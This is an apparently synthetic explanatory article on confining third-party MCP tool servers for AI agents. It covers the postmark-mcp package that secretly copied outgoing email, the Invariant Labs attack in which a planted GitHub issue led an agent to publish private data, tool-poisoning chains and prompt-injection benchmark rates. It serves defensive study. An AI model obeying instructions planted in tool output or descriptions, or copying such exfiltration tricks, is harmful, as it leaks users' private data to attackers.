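# Confining the third-party tools and plugin servers that AI agents use

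## Tool servers, and what it means to confine one

An AI agent is a language model that acts in a loop: it calls a tool, reads the reply, and then calls another tool or answers its user. The tools are ordinary programs that do things like search the web, query a database, read a calendar, or convert files, and many come from developers the user knows nothing about. The agent gives each tool the data it needs, so a person who asks an agent to turn a contract into a PDF may be giving that contract to code written by a stranger.

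A tool is confined if it can use the data it is given and answer the person who started it, but cannot pass the data to anyone else. Butler Lampson, then at Xerox's research centre in Palo Alto, described the problem of confining programs in 1973, and an operating system called KeyKOS had a working solution in the 1980s.

Third-party tools mostly reach agents through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard that Anthropic, the developer of the Claude models, published in November 2024. MCP defines the format of messages between the program that runs an agent and the programs that offer it tools. The project's main software kits are downloaded close to half a billion times a month, according to the post announcing the current version (Model Context Protocol, 2026). Automated builds inflate such counts, but the standard is clearly in wide use.

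### How an agent calls a tool

The client application is the program that runs the agent, such as a chat program or a code editor. It connects the agent to tools and enforces the user's settings. Model Context Protocol (MCP) documents call it the host. A tool server is a program that offers one or more tools. MCP's *Architecture* (2026) makes the client application responsible for enforcing security policy and obtaining consent, and has it open a separate connection to each server.

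Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026) illustrates the message flow with a weather tool. The client application asks the server for its list of tools. For each tool, the server returns a name (`get_weather`), a description ("Get current weather information for a location") and a schema of the arguments it accepts, in this case only a city name or zip code. The client application adds these entries to the text that the model reads. When the user asks about the weather in New York, the model writes a call with the tool's name and the argument "New York", and the client application sends it to the server. The server runs whatever code its developer wrote and returns a reply, 72°F and partly cloudy, which the client application adds to the model's text. The model has no connection of its own to the server, so every message between them passes through the client application.

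The server's developer controls two pieces of text that the model reads in this exchange, the description and the reply, and can use either to try to steer the model. A server may also attach annotations, which are machine-readable notes on how a tool behaves. The specification requires client applications to treat these as untrusted unless they trust the server. The list of tools can also change, and the description a user saw at installation may differ from the one the model reads a month later.

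In the other direction, the server receives the arguments and little else. One of MCP's design principles is that a server should not be able to read the whole conversation or see into other servers. This protection ends at delivery, because the protocol limits what the client application sends to a server but has no rule that could limit where the server sends it next. To prevent leaks, the specification also recommends that client applications show the user a tool's inputs before the call goes out. The user can then see that the converter will receive the contract, but not whether the converter will send it elsewhere.

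### Local servers and remote ones

A tool server can run locally or remotely. A local server is a process on the user's machine. The client application launches it with a command from a settings file and exchanges messages with it over its standard input and output streams. A remote server runs on someone else's machine, and the client application reaches it over the web.

By default, a process that the user's program launches gets the user's rights. According to the security blog easy-sec-blog, a local tool server can therefore reach the user's files, environment variables (where developers often keep passwords for online services), login keys and browser sessions. This access doesn't depend on what the tool is for, so a unit converter gets the same access as a backup program.

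A local MCP server can open network connections like any other program the user runs. This is easy to miss because descriptions of MCP tend to concentrate on the connection between the client application and the server. For example, a comparison table in Hugging Face's *MCP Key Concepts and Architecture* lists "None" under network and "No exposure" under security for a local server. Those entries are right about the connection, which never leaves the machine, but wrong about the server itself.

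A remote server starts out with less access than a local one. It cannot touch the user's disk and sees only what the client application sends it. But its operator chooses the machine, the code and the storage, and can change any of them without notice. A local server starts out with far too much access, but the user can take that access away, which they cannot do with a remote server.

### What a server can send besides a reply

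A tool sometimes needs more input during a call, such as a missing detail or a confirmation. Before July 2026, a server could send the client application its own request while the original call stayed open. *Designing requestState for Multi Round-Trip Requests* (Körbächer, 2026) describes three such requests. A server could use elicitation to ask the user a question, sampling to use the client application's language model, and roots to get the list of directories that the client application exposed to it.

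The current specification, dated 28 July 2026, replaced that back-channel with another. Model Context Protocol's *Multi-round-trip requests*, a documentation page for Python developers, summarizes the new approach as "Return, don't call back." A server that needs more input now ends the call early and returns an `input_required` result containing its requests. The client application collects the answers and repeats the original call with them attached. Under Model Context Protocol's *Multi Round-Trip Requests*, a server may include only the kinds of request for which the client application has declared support, and it must not assume that the client application will comply. A client application can therefore switch off a whole kind of request by not declaring support for it.

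The same revision's list of changes (Model Context Protocol, 2026) deprecated three features. They will still work for at least twelve months, but new software should not adopt them. *A More Predictable Release Cycle for MCP* (Delimarsky and Soria Parra, 2026) gave 30 March 2027 as the target for the next version.

| What the server sends | Effect | Status in the July 2026 specification |
|---|---|---|
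| Elicitation | Puts a question to the user, in a form or on a web page | Kept |
| Sampling | Has the client application run its model on text from the server and return the output | Deprecated |
| Roots | Obtains the list of directories open to the server | Deprecated |
| Log messages | Reports on the server's activity, if the client application opted in | Deprecated |
| Change notices | Signal that the list of tools has changed, if the client application subscribed | Kept |

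Deprecating roots and sampling has mixed effects on confinement. In place of roots, the maintainers suggest passing a directory or file in the call's arguments or the server's settings, which is an improvement if the server then gets only what it needs. In place of sampling, they suggest that servers connect directly to a model provider. This is worse, because a server that used the client application's model could work without a network connection. Connecting to a provider requires network access and an account, and it sends the user's data to a company the user may never have chosen. Sampling could also leak data, though. One of its options, now also deprecated, let a server request that the client application add context from all connected servers to the prompt, and the model's answer could then carry one server's data to another.

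Elicitation deserves attention because it is staying in MCP and its use is spreading. It became generally available in Claude in November (Anthropic, *MCP servers can now ship skills, run tasks, and more with Claude*, 2026). A form that asks for a user name only brings data into the server. In the web-page version, the server supplies an address for the user to open, and that address can carry data out. For example, a converter that has just read a contract could encode a clause of it in the link. An ordinary reply can do something similar, because MCP lets a tool return links for the client application to fetch.

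### Confinement and the factory

Lampson's paper, *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, is about a customer who runs someone else's program on private data. The customer wants the program's answer but wants nothing about the data to reach the program's owner. Lampson called a program confined if it could pass information only to its caller, and listed ways an ordinary program can violate that condition. It can write the data to a file in its owner's directory or send a message to another process that the owner controls. If it has memory that lasts between calls, it can store the data and return it in a normal reply when the owner calls. It can also hide a few bits in the bill for its services.

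He also saw that confinement has to extend to everything a program calls. If a confined program can call a second program that is neither trusted nor confined, the second program can leak the data it receives. The same is true of an agent's tool that relies on another online service.

KeyKOS, which Norman Hardy and his colleagues developed for IBM mainframes, let a caller check whether a program was confined. It was built on capabilities, which are unforgeable references to resources that also carry the right to use them. A program can use a file if it holds the capability for that file, but without a capability for the network it cannot even attempt a connection. (MCP's documents use "capability" in an unrelated sense, for a feature that a client application or server declares.) The capabilities a program starts with and those it later receives therefore determine its authority, meaning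 everything it can do to or through the world outside itself.

The factory was a trusted service built on this. A developer gave it a program and the capabilities that every copy should start with, then sealed the factory. A customer who wanted to use the program asked the factory for a fresh copy, which ran in storage the customer supplied. The customer could first ask whether such copies had any outward authority. The factory answered by checking the list of capabilities, without examining the code, which might be long or secret, and the customer did not have to trust the developer. Customer and developer both had to trust the factory, but it is one small program that many people can inspect, and they only have to do so once.

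A confined program can have plenty of storage, as long as only that copy of the program and its caller can ever read it. A converter, for example, can safely write half-finished pages to a private scratch file. If the file is in a folder that another program can read, or one that synchronises to a company's cloud account, it is as useful to a thief as a network connection. Data can also leak if one copy of the converter serves two customers and keeps its files in between, because the second customer's reply can then contain the first customer's contract, which is Lampson's case of the program with a memory.

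Since July 2026, the MCP protocol itself has kept no session between calls, which has, probably by accident, made it easier to use fresh copies of a server. A server that needs to ask the user a question can put its working state in the result, and the client application returns that state unopened with the next attempt. Tools that keep something like a shopping cart still need persistent storage. For many others, a client application could start a new copy for every call and delete it afterwards.

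### Four questions to ask of any tool

Lampson's leaks and the factory's check reduce to four questions, which apply whether a tool runs on a laptop or in a data centre.

1. Who starts the tool? Whoever starts a program decides what it starts with. If the user's client application does it, the user's settings can count for something. If the tool's operator does it, they cannot.
2. Which network, storage and callback authority does it begin with? Network authority covers any address that the program can contact, including harmless-looking ones. For storage, what matters is who else can read it and how long it lasts. Callback authority is what the tool can bring about through the client application, such as a question to the user or a run of the model.
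3. Who can verify that? The developer's word is worth little here, because a dishonest developer would say the same thing. A setting that the user's own software enforces is much better, and a trusted service that can report on each copy before any data goes in is better still.
4. What does its reply reach? Confinement permits a tool to answer its caller. If the caller is an agent with an email account, the answer may travel a long way.

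MCP gives a client application no way to verify that a server is confined. The client can ask which protocol versions and features the server supports, but no protocol message establishes whether the server has a network connection, and annotations are only the server's description of itself. Any assurance of confinement has to come from whatever starts the server.

### A converter and a confidential contract

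Suppose a lawyer's client is about to buy another company, and neither company has announced the deal. The lawyer has the contract as a word-processor file and asks an agent to convert it to PDF using a local MCP server that a stranger published.

In the usual arrangement, the lawyer has pasted a command into the client application's settings. The client application runs that command, which starts the converter with the lawyer's permissions. The agent calls the converter with the location of the contract. The converter, which can open any of the lawyer's files, opens the contract, writes a PDF next to it, and returns the PDF's location. If the developer has added a few lines that upload every document to a server abroad, the lawyer sees the same PDF and the same reply. The client application started this tool, so the answer to the first question is encouraging, but it gave the converter access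 to the whole network and the whole disk. The only way to verify that the converter doesn't misuse that access is to read its code, and to read it again after each update.

Now suppose that the client application gets its converters from a factory. Before sending anything, it queries the factory about whether new copies have any outward authority. The factory checks what each copy receives (the converter's own code and a set of fonts, all read-only) and reports that they have none. The client application then supplies private scratch storage and sends the contract's contents instead of its location, so the converter doesn't need to open the lawyer's files and has no way to. The converter returns a PDF, and the client application deletes that copy of the converter along with its scratch storage. The dishonest developer's extra lines are still in the code, but they fail because they have no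 network access. Removing authority does not close covert channels. For example, a converter could still vary its running time or processor load in a pattern that another program on the machine can detect.

MCP is gaining some support for sending file contents. *Exploring File Uploads and Downloads in MCP* (Delimarsky and St. Charles, 2026) describes an experimental extension in which the server marks an argument as a file and the client application, after the user approves, fills it in without the model having to handle the bytes. A small file can travel inside the call. A larger one goes to separate storage, and someone has to check who else can read that storage. The user's approval covers sending the file but doesn't limit what the converter can do with it afterwards, so it does not replace the factory's check.

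The factory's converter is also less useful than the ordinary one. If the contract's letterhead is a picture on a website, the converter cannot fetch it, so the PDF will have a blank space unless the client application fetches the picture first. If the developer wants each copy to contact a licensing service, the factory will report that copies have outward authority, and the lawyer must either refuse the tool or use it unconfined. A converter can still do its main job within these limits, but a web search tool cannot.

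The converter can still do harm through its reply. If the agent reads the text of the PDF, a malicious converter can add a sentence telling it to email the contract to some address, and the agent may follow that sentence as if it were an instruction from its user. This is called prompt injection. The converter would still be confined by Lampson's definition, since it gave the data only to its caller. The danger comes from the agent's other tools. Simon Willison calls the combination of private data, untrusted content and a way to communicate externally the lethal trifecta. Model Context Protocol (2026) concluded in a March post on tool annotations that when users mix tools from several servers, the risk depends on the whole session and cannot be judged from any one server. The client application could prevent the injection by saving the PDF without showing it to the model, but the PDF might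 still contain a link with part of the contract encoded in its address, which would leak that part if someone clicked on it.

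## The postmark-mcp package: an email tool that copied every message

Unlike a document converter, a tool that sends email needs a network connection to do its main job. In September 2025 the security company Koi reported what it called the first malicious MCP server in real use, an email tool named postmark-mcp. It sent users' messages as they asked but added a hidden recipient.

### Fifteen clean versions in two days

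Postmark is a commercial service that delivers email for other companies' software. Its owner, ActiveCampaign, keeps the code of an MCP server for the service on the code-sharing site GitHub, but had not published it on npm, the public registry that supplies most JavaScript packages. An unrelated developer copied the code and published it on npm under the same name, so the copy looked like the official tool. Postmark later said it had no involvement with the package. Impersonating a server is often this easy, and *MCP-38* (2026), a catalogue of threats to MCP systems, lists registries that don't check the identity of whoever registers a server.

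The developer uploaded the first version on 15 September 2025. By Koi's count, fifteen versions worked as they should. Version 1.0.16, released on 17 September, added one line that copied outgoing mail to an address at giftshop.club, a domain Koi thought was another of the developer's side projects. Koi's monitoring software flagged the change. Koi contacted the developer, who did not reply but deleted the package from npm. On 26 September the package appeared in a public database of malicious code, as OSV's *MAL-2025-47604* (2025).

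Idan Dardikman, Koi's chief technology officer, pointed out in Infosecurity Magazine's *Malicious AI Agent Server Reportedly Steals Emails* that deleting the package did not protect people who had already installed it. Installed copies kept running and copying mail until users removed them.

Snyk's *Malicious MCP Server on npm postmark-mcp Harvests Emails* (2025) dates every version of the package, clean and malicious, to between 15 and 17 September. The package therefore had little time to build a track record, although Koi presented the case as a betrayal of trust built up over a long time and warned that a tool can be legitimate for months before it turns malicious. That can happen, but users probably trusted this package because it had Postmark's name and Postmark's working code. The developer's profile would not have warned them either, since Koi found a software engineer using his real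 name, with legitimate projects on GitHub.

The number of victims is uncertain. Koi started from 1,500 downloads a week, assumed that a fifth were in active use, and arrived at about 300 organisations sending 3,000 to 15,000 emails a day between them. Koi called this a guess. The Hacker News (2025) reported 1,643 downloads in total, some of which were probably automated. Infosecurity Magazine's figure of 15,000 users looks like a mistake, because the article also gives 300 organisations, which is a fifth of 1,500.

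### What the added line did

Snyk published the full code of version 1.0.18, the last release. The agent calls `sendEmail`, one of the server's four tools, with a recipient, a subject and a text, plus optional fields such as attachments. The server copies these into a single request and adds a `Bcc` (blind carbon copy) field containing the giftshop.club address. It sends the request to Postmark, which delivers one copy to the intended recipient and another to that address. The agent gets back a success message with an ID, the intended recipient and the subject.

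The package copied fewer messages than most accounts suggest. A second tool, `sendEmailWithTemplate`, fills in a template stored at Postmark and has no `Bcc` field in its code. The other two tools list templates and report delivery statistics. This line would not have copied any mail from an organisation that sent only templated messages, although that organisation would still have been running the same stranger's code.

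### The four questions

The user's client application started postmark-mcp, so the user could have limited the package's access at launch. Few people set such limits. The usual settings file contains a command that downloads the package from npm and runs it with all of the user's permissions.

The server could therefore contact any address and open any file that the user could open. It also read the user's Postmark token from its environment. This secret let it send mail from the account and access the account's templates and statistics. The published code never uses the client application to question the user or run the model, but nothing in the setup prevented this.

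Verifying the package's behaviour required reading each version published on npm. Reading Postmark's project on GitHub would not have helped, because the code there was clean. The version number that the server reported to client applications would not have helped either, because it was still 1.0.0 in version 1.0.18.

The reply did no harm to the agent, and the attack involved no prompt injection. The model did what the user wanted and the mail still leaked, so a more careful model would not have prevented it.

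### Why the usual controls would have failed

If the client application had shown the user every call before sending it, as the MCP specification recommends, the user would have seen the right recipient, subject and text. A program that checks the traffic automatically has the same limitation. In Herkos' *The malicious server*, the developer of one such program concluded that it would not have caught the copying, because the hidden address appears only in the server's own request to Postmark.

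Cutting off the server's network connection would have stopped the theft, but only by disabling the tool. The server checks the token with Postmark at startup. If that check fails, the process exits before connecting to the client application, and the agent has no email tool.

An address allowlist that let the server contact only Postmark would not have stopped the copying. The published code put the hidden recipient in a field of an ordinary request to Postmark, which the allowlist would have to permit. Herkos ends by suggesting that an allowlist would close the gap, but that is wrong for this package. Snyk's advice to block giftshop.club on the user's network has a similar problem, because Postmark's machines delivered the mail to that domain and the user's machine never contacted it. An allowlist would still have helped against a simpler attack that uploaded files to the attacker's own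 server, but it would have broken a legitimate feature, because `sendEmail` downloads attachments from whatever web address the agent gives it.

Running the server in a container would have protected the user's other files, which the published code leaves alone.

### Checking recipients in each request

The hidden copy was plainly visible in one place, the request from the server to Postmark. A trusted layer at that point could have stopped it, provided that it read the contents of each request as well as the destination. Suppose the lawyer from the converter example asks an agent to email the finished PDF to a client:

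1. The client application shows the lawyer the recipient's address, the lawyer approves it, and the client application passes that address to the layer.
2. The server builds its request and sends it to the layer, which is the only address it can contact.
3. The layer reads every recipient field (`To`, `Cc` and `Bcc`) and finds an address at giftshop.club that the lawyer never named.
4. The layer refuses the request and tells the lawyer why. If the recipients had matched, it would have added the Postmark token and forwarded the message.

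This works only if the approved list comes from the user. If the layer accepted whatever the model wrote in the call, a prompt injection could put the attacker's address in the `To` field and the check would pass. Requests to Postmark are normally encrypted, so the layer can read them only if the server sends them to the layer directly or accepts the layer's certificate. The layer also has to handle every kind of request that can send mail, including those that use templates, and refuse any it cannot read.

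Once such a layer exists, there is little reason for the server to send anything itself. A confined server with no network connection could compose the message and return it for the layer to send. Most of `sendEmail` only rearranges its arguments and fetches attachments, so the user would lose little by dropping the third-party code altogether. But someone trusted would have to write and maintain a sender for each mail provider.

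### What is left to confine

An email tool cannot be confined under Lampson's definition, because its purpose is to pass information to someone other than its caller. A factory would not help the user choose between Postmark's clean code and the malicious copy, because it would report outward authority for both. The useful limits for such a tool are on what it sends and who receives it.

| What can be limited | What version 1.0.18 could do | What a trusted layer could enforce |
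|---|---|---|
| Recipients | Add any address to any message | Only the addresses that the user named |
| Content | Change the text after the user approved it | The text sent matches the text approved |
| Attachments | Download files from any web address | The client application supplies the files |
| Credentials | Read the Postmark token and use it freely | The layer keeps the token and adds it after the check |

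An email can leak information even when it goes only to the right recipients. A malicious server could encode part of the message in the address of an image, as the converter could in a link, and the attacker would receive that part when the recipient's mail program fetched the image. Comparing the outgoing text with the approved text would catch this. But if the agent itself wrote a confidential paragraph into a message to an approved recipient, the user would have to notice it when reading the draft, because the two texts would match.

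Keeping the token away from the server probably takes the least effort of the four. Someone who stole the token could keep sending mail as the user from another machine after the package was removed, so Snyk told users to replace their tokens.

### Malicious servers in the laboratory

To study how easily other servers could do the same, Zhao, Liu and colleagues (2025) built malicious servers themselves in *When MCP Servers Attack*. They identified twelve categories of attack based on the parts of a server, such as its launch command, startup code, tool descriptions, tool code and replies, and wrote one server for each category. They tested the servers on ten pairings of three client applications (Claude Desktop, the code editor Cursor and one built on the open-source framework fast-agent) with five models. Each attack ran fifteen times per pairing, always in a new conversation. An attack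 counted as successful if it achieved its purpose without the client application or the model blocking it.

Six of the twelve servers succeeded in every trial. One of the six hid its attack in the tool's code, as postmark-mcp did, and four others also relied on malicious code or an unsafe launch command. The sixth put harmful content in the tool's reply, which every model passed on. (Cursor could not run some of the tests, so two of the six perfect scores rest on six pairings instead of ten.)

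Attacks that had to persuade the model were less consistent. A misleading tool description worked in 89.3% of trials on average, but it never worked on GPT-4o in Cursor. In fast-agent, the success rate of this attack fell from 100% to 6.7% when the model was given Cursor's system prompt, the standing instructions a client application gives its model. The models date from 2025, and newer ones may resist persuasion better. That would not stop an attack in the tool's code, which doesn't depend on persuading the model.

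The same team tested whether scanners would catch such servers before anyone used them. They generated 120 malicious servers, ten per category, and ran two popular scanners on them. mcp-scan detected four, all with poisoned tool descriptions, and missed all ten servers with malicious tool code. Snyk had recommended mcp-scan in its post about postmark-mcp, while conceding that this attack was an ordinary backdoor in code. Tencent's AI-Infra-Guard, which uses a language model to read the source, caught seven of the ten servers with malicious tool code. Each scan took about ten minutes and cost around fifty cents, and results varied between runs.

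The researchers installed these laboratory servers on purpose. The study shows what a malicious server can do once someone runs it, but not how many exist or how often people install them.

### Servers that turn bad after an update

A user who set up postmark-mcp on 16 September got a clean version but may have been running a malicious one two days later without changing anything. Many launch commands fetch the newest version of a package each time the client application starts, and Zhao and colleagues note that most client applications start every configured server automatically.

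The simplest remedy is to pin the version, which means naming an exact release in the settings so that the user decides when to update. Pinning would have protected anyone who had chosen a version up to 1.0.15, but not those who first installed the package after 17 September and pinned the newest release. The developer of Herkos ran its configuration scanner on a typical postmark-mcp set-up and got two warnings, one for the unpinned package and one for launching it directly. Both disappeared after the developer pinned the version and routed the calls through Herkos. The scan examines how the user installed a package, so a pinned copy of 1.0.18 would pass it too.

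Monitoring changes in what a server advertises would have missed postmark-mcp. Snyk found no notable difference between versions 1.0.15 and 1.0.18 except the added line, which left the tool's name, description and arguments as they were. An alarm on every advertised change would also go off constantly, presumably mostly for routine development. Kraishan (2026), in *Same Name, Different Server*, collected the entire public MCP registry as it stood in August 2026, with 21,643 servers and 72,606 version records. Among servers with more than one version, 51.1% had changed what they advertise, 40.6% silently, and 4.2% had moved their remote endpoint to a different host under the same registry identity. MCP does not notify installed client applications of such a move.

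Malicious code can also run before the client application starts the server. In June 2026 the same public database listed an npm package called mcp-server-postgres, which impersonated the official MCP server for the Postgres database (OSV, *MAL-2026-5481*, 2026). Its code ran as soon as a user installed it and sent out a message containing the name of the user's machine. Confining the server at launch would have been too late, so the installation has to run under the same restrictions as the tool.

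## The GitHub server attack: the language model carries the data

The postmark-mcp theft depended on a line of malicious code that anyone who read the code could have found. In May 2025, two researchers at Invariant Labs, a security company in Zurich, showed that an agent can leak private data even when none of its tools are malicious. Their report, *GitHub MCP Exploited*, describes how they got an agent to copy a user's private information to a public page through GitHub's own tool server.

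### A planted issue

GitHub keeps projects in repositories, which can be public or private. On a public repository, any GitHub user can post an issue, which is a bug report or a request. People propose changes to a project's files in pull requests, which anyone can read if the repository is public.

The researchers set up an account with a public repository, which held a simple version of Pac-Man, and private ones, which held personal projects and details about the account's owner. They connected the account to Claude Desktop, Anthropic's chat program, through GitHub's MCP server and used Claude 4 Opus as the model. Then they played the attacker and posted an issue on the Pac-Man repository. They worded it as a friendly suggestion to give the author more credit and included a request for details from the author's other repositories.

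The leak took four steps:

1. The user asked the agent to look at the open issues on the public repository.
2. The agent called the server, which returned the issues, including the planted one.
3. The model treated the planted text as a request to carry out and called the server again to read the private repositories.
4. The model then had the server open a pull request on the Pac-Man repository with the private details in it.

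Anyone on the internet could now read the names of private repositories, the owner's plan to move to South America, and the owner's salary.

No part of the system exceeded its permissions. The server could read the private repositories because it works with the user's own account, as heise's *Attack via GitHub MCP server* explains. Invariant Labs concluded that GitHub could not fix the problem by changing the server. An address allowlist would not have helped either, because GitHub was both the source of the data and the place it leaked to.

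The user had a chance to stop the leak, because Claude Desktop asks the user to confirm each tool call by default. Someone who had asked only about open issues might have wondered why the agent was trying to read private files. But the researchers pointed out that many users choose "Always Allow" and stop watching.

They proposed a rule that limits an agent to one repository per session. It would have stopped the attack at the third step, without having to judge whether any text was malicious. But it also prevents the agent from doing jobs that span repositories, such as carrying a fix from one project to another. The published rule also covers only GitHub calls. If the agent had a calendar tool as well, an attacker could still plant an issue telling it to put the user's appointments in a public pull request.

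### The lethal trifecta

Three weeks later Simon Willison, a programmer who helped coin the term prompt injection, used the GitHub attack as an example in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (Willison, 2025). He points out that GitHub's server gave the agent all three parts of the trifecta by letting it read private repositories, fetch issues written by strangers, and open public pull requests.

The weakness exists because the user's request, the tool descriptions and the tools' replies all reach the model as one sequence of text, and the model cannot reliably tell which parts came from someone entitled to give it instructions. Willison thinks MCP makes the problem worse because it encourages people to combine tools from different makers. A company that finds such a leak in its own product can usually block the channel through which data leaves, but no single vendor can do that when users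 combine the tools themselves.

Willison is also suspicious of products that filter out malicious instructions. Sellers tend to claim that these products catch 95% of attacks, which he calls "very much a failing grade" in web security. Attackers can try again, so if a filter stops 95% of attempts and the attempts are independent, an attacker has a better than even chance of getting through within 14 tries.

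Attackers who adapt to a defence do better still. Willison (2025), in *New prompt injection papers*, summarises *The Attacker Moves Second*, an October 2025 paper by fourteen researchers, some of them from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind. They tested twelve published defences against prompt injection and jailbreaks, revising their attacks in response to each one. The attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the twelve, although the original publications had reported rates near zero for the majority of those defences. Human attackers, recruited through a contest with 500 participants, beat all twelve.

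The Economist argued in September 2025 that AI developers should learn from Victorian engineers, who built in redundancy because they could not trust their iron. Willison, in *30 posts tagged "lethal-trifecta"*, replied that this doesn't work for security, where even 99% is a failing grade. Extra iron protects against random flaws because several beams are unlikely to fail together by chance, but an attacker looks for the one input that gets past every layer. Redundancy still makes the attacker's job harder, but it can't provide the safety margin it gives a bridge.

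The lethal trifecta covers only data theft, as Willison acknowledges, so it does not address planted instructions that make an agent delete files. His advice to avoid the combination is also hard to follow, because many of the most useful agents need all three parts. An email assistant, for example, has to read private mail, some of it from strangers, and send replies.

### Meta's Rule of Two

Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) turns the trifecta into a design rule. Until prompt injection can be reliably detected and refused, an agent should have at most two of these three properties in any one session: (A) it can process untrustworthy inputs, (B) it has access to sensitive systems or private data, and (C) it can change state or communicate externally. If a task needs all three, the agent needs supervision, which normally means that a person approves its actions.

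Meta gives several hypothetical examples:

| Agent | Properties it keeps | How its designers limit the remaining one |
|---|---|---|
| Travel assistant | A and B | A person confirms every booking or payment, and the agent opens only web addresses that come from trusted sources |
| Web research assistant | A and C | The browser runs in a sandbox without the user's logins |
| Internal coding agent | B and C | The system filters the agent's data sources by author |

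An agent can also change its combination during a session. It might begin by researching on the open web with no private data, then permanently lose its outward connection before it opens internal files. A malicious page it had read could still distort its answer, but the agent could not send the files anywhere.

Willison welcomed the rule because "change state" covers harms that the trifecta leaves out. But Meta's diagram marked every pair of properties as "Safe", and he objected on Hacker News (as simonw) that an agent with untrusted input and the power to change things can do harm without seeing any private data. Meta's team accepted the point and changed the label.

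The approval step is a weaker safeguard than it looks. According to Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* (2026), users of its coding agent, Claude Code, approved about 93% of permission requests and became less attentive as they saw more of them. That rate might only mean that most requests were harmless. But Willison reports that Anthropic later ran a test with 1,053 paid participants, in which it replaced one request in each session with a clearly dangerous command, and only 13.6% refused it.

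It is also hard to say where a session ends. Many agents now keep notes between sessions, and Anthropic warns that an injection saved in such notes loads again every time the agent starts. An agent could read a malicious web page on Monday, when it has no private data, and save a note about it. On Tuesday it could open that note alongside the user's files. Each session would satisfy the Rule of Two, but the attack would have all three properties across the two sessions.

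It is also not always clear which inputs to trust. In February 2026 a member of Anthropic's internal red team, which stages attacks to find weaknesses, emailed an employee a prompt to paste into Claude Code. The prompt looked like routine instructions, but one step was to read the employee's cloud passwords and send them to an outside address. The researchers ran the prompt 25 times, and Claude sent the passwords 24 times. A designer applying the Rule of Two would probably have counted the user's own prompt as trusted.

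### How one tool can misuse another

In the GitHub attack, the malicious text came from a stranger's issue. Invariant Labs distinguishes its GitHub attack from tool poisoning, in which the tool itself is compromised. In tool poisoning, the attacker puts instructions for the model in the tool's description or replies. If the client application has also connected the agent to other servers, those instructions can direct the model to use the other servers' tools.

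Suppose the lawyer from the converter example also has a currency tool from an unknown developer and an honest email tool. The currency tool is confined. It has no network connection, and the only file it can access is a read-only list of exchange rates that the client application supplies. It receives only an amount and two currency codes. The contract price is in euros, and the lawyer wants it in dollars.

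1. When the session starts, the client application collects the descriptions of both tools and adds them to the text that the model reads.
2. The currency tool's description explains how to convert an amount. It also claims that the law requires a copy of the source document to go to a certain email address before each conversion.
3. The lawyer asks for the price in dollars. The model has already read the contract, so it has the full text available.
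4. The model follows the description and calls the email tool, with the contract in the message and the attacker's address as the recipient.
5. The email tool sends the message, as it would any other.
6. The model calls the currency tool with the amount, and the lawyer gets the right answer.

The currency tool stole a document without ever receiving it. A factory would have correctly reported that the tool had no outward authority. The email tool's developer did nothing wrong, and reading that tool's code would have revealed no problem. The two servers never exchanged a message. The model carried the data from one to the other.

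The same trick can work through a tool's reply. The currency tool could have a clean description and answer its first few calls normally, then add the instruction to a later answer. A scanner that checks descriptions at installation would miss this. The user would also be less likely to notice, since people rarely read the raw text a tool returns to the model.

The client application is the best place to stop such attacks, because it passes on every message between the model and the tools. It could keep a tool by an unknown developer out of any session that has an email tool. Or it could refuse the call in step 4 if the recipient is not an address the lawyer has named, as the trusted layer in the postmark-mcp case would.

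### How often models resist

These attacks succeed much less often against newer models than against the one in the GitHub demonstration. In May 2026 Anthropic reported results for Claude Opus 4.7 on Agent Red Teaming, a prompt-injection test by the security company Gray Swan. Single attacks succeeded about 0.1% of the time, and the rate rose to around 5–6% when attackers could make 100 attempts and adapt as they went.

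Developers have since moved to harder tests because their newest models were scoring close to the maximum on the old ones. Anthropic replaced the Agent Red Teaming benchmark for that reason, according to TechFeed. The new benchmark has 28 scenarios and 1,130 attacks, and Anthropic developed it with Gray Swan and the British and American government institutes that test AI models. In July, Schneier (2026) quoted results for Claude Opus 5 and OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol in *Anthropic's Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection*. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* gives results for an older model on a Gray Swan test.

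The last column below shows what the repeated rate would be if attempts were independent and each succeeded at the single-attempt rate *p*. For *n* attempts, that is 1 − (1 − *p*)ⁿ.

| Model | One attempt | Repeated attempts | If attempts were independent |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 4.7% | 63% within 100 | 99% |
| Claude Opus 4.7 | about 0.1% | 5–6% within 100 | about 10% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 0.2% | 2.0% within 15 | 3% |
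| GPT-5.6 Sol | 3.1% | 20.0% within 15 | 38% |

In every row, the measured rate is lower than it would be if attempts were independent, probably because attacks succeed quickly in some scenarios and fail on every attempt in others. If so, the average is a poor guide to any particular set-up. A user whose agent resembles one of the weak scenarios faces a much higher risk than the published figure, and has no easy way to find out.

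Even a low success rate can produce many victims. If an attacker sent one malicious email to each of a million people's agents and 0.1% of the emails worked, there would be a thousand victims. Real mass mailings would probably succeed less often, since benchmark attacks tend to be strong.

In late 2026 Gray Swan started publishing its own comparisons of how well models resist attacks. Google's Gemini 4 Argon did best, with attackers succeeding 2.3% of the time within 15 attacks, and Nvidia's open-weight Nemotron 3.5 Super VL did worst, at 94.3%, according to iAfrica's *New Independent Tracker Finds Wide Safety Gaps Between AI Models*. A user who connects an agent to many outside tools can therefore cut the risk substantially just by switching models.

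Attack success rates also depend on the test. PromptArmor's *FrontierBreach* uses long office tasks, such as analysing a bond portfolio and recommending a trading strategy. Attacks in that test succeeded in 10.0% of cases on Opus 5 and 33.3% on GPT-5.6 Sol. On the benchmark that Schneier quoted, the rate for Opus 5 was 2.0% within 15 attempts. PromptArmor sells security services, so it has an interest in finding weaknesses, just as model developers have an interest in low numbers. But long tasks full of outside documents are closer to what people want agents for.

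The route of the attack also matters. According to TechRepublic's *OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026), OpenAI found that GPT-5.6 Sol failed on about 0.05% of attacks that came directly through chat, but on 3.77% of those in content from tools and other outside sources, which is the relevant figure for tool servers.

Some tests have found no successful attacks. Anthropic commissioned Trajectory Labs to attack Claude Code in auto mode, in which a second model decides which actions to allow, and all 720 attempts failed. But these were 72 scenarios run ten times each. If all the attempts were independent, the upper limit on the true success rate would be 0.4% at 95% confidence. If the ten runs of a scenario tend to turn out the same way, it makes more sense to count 72 trials, which raises the limit to about 4%. Both limits apply only to attacks like the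 ones in the test.

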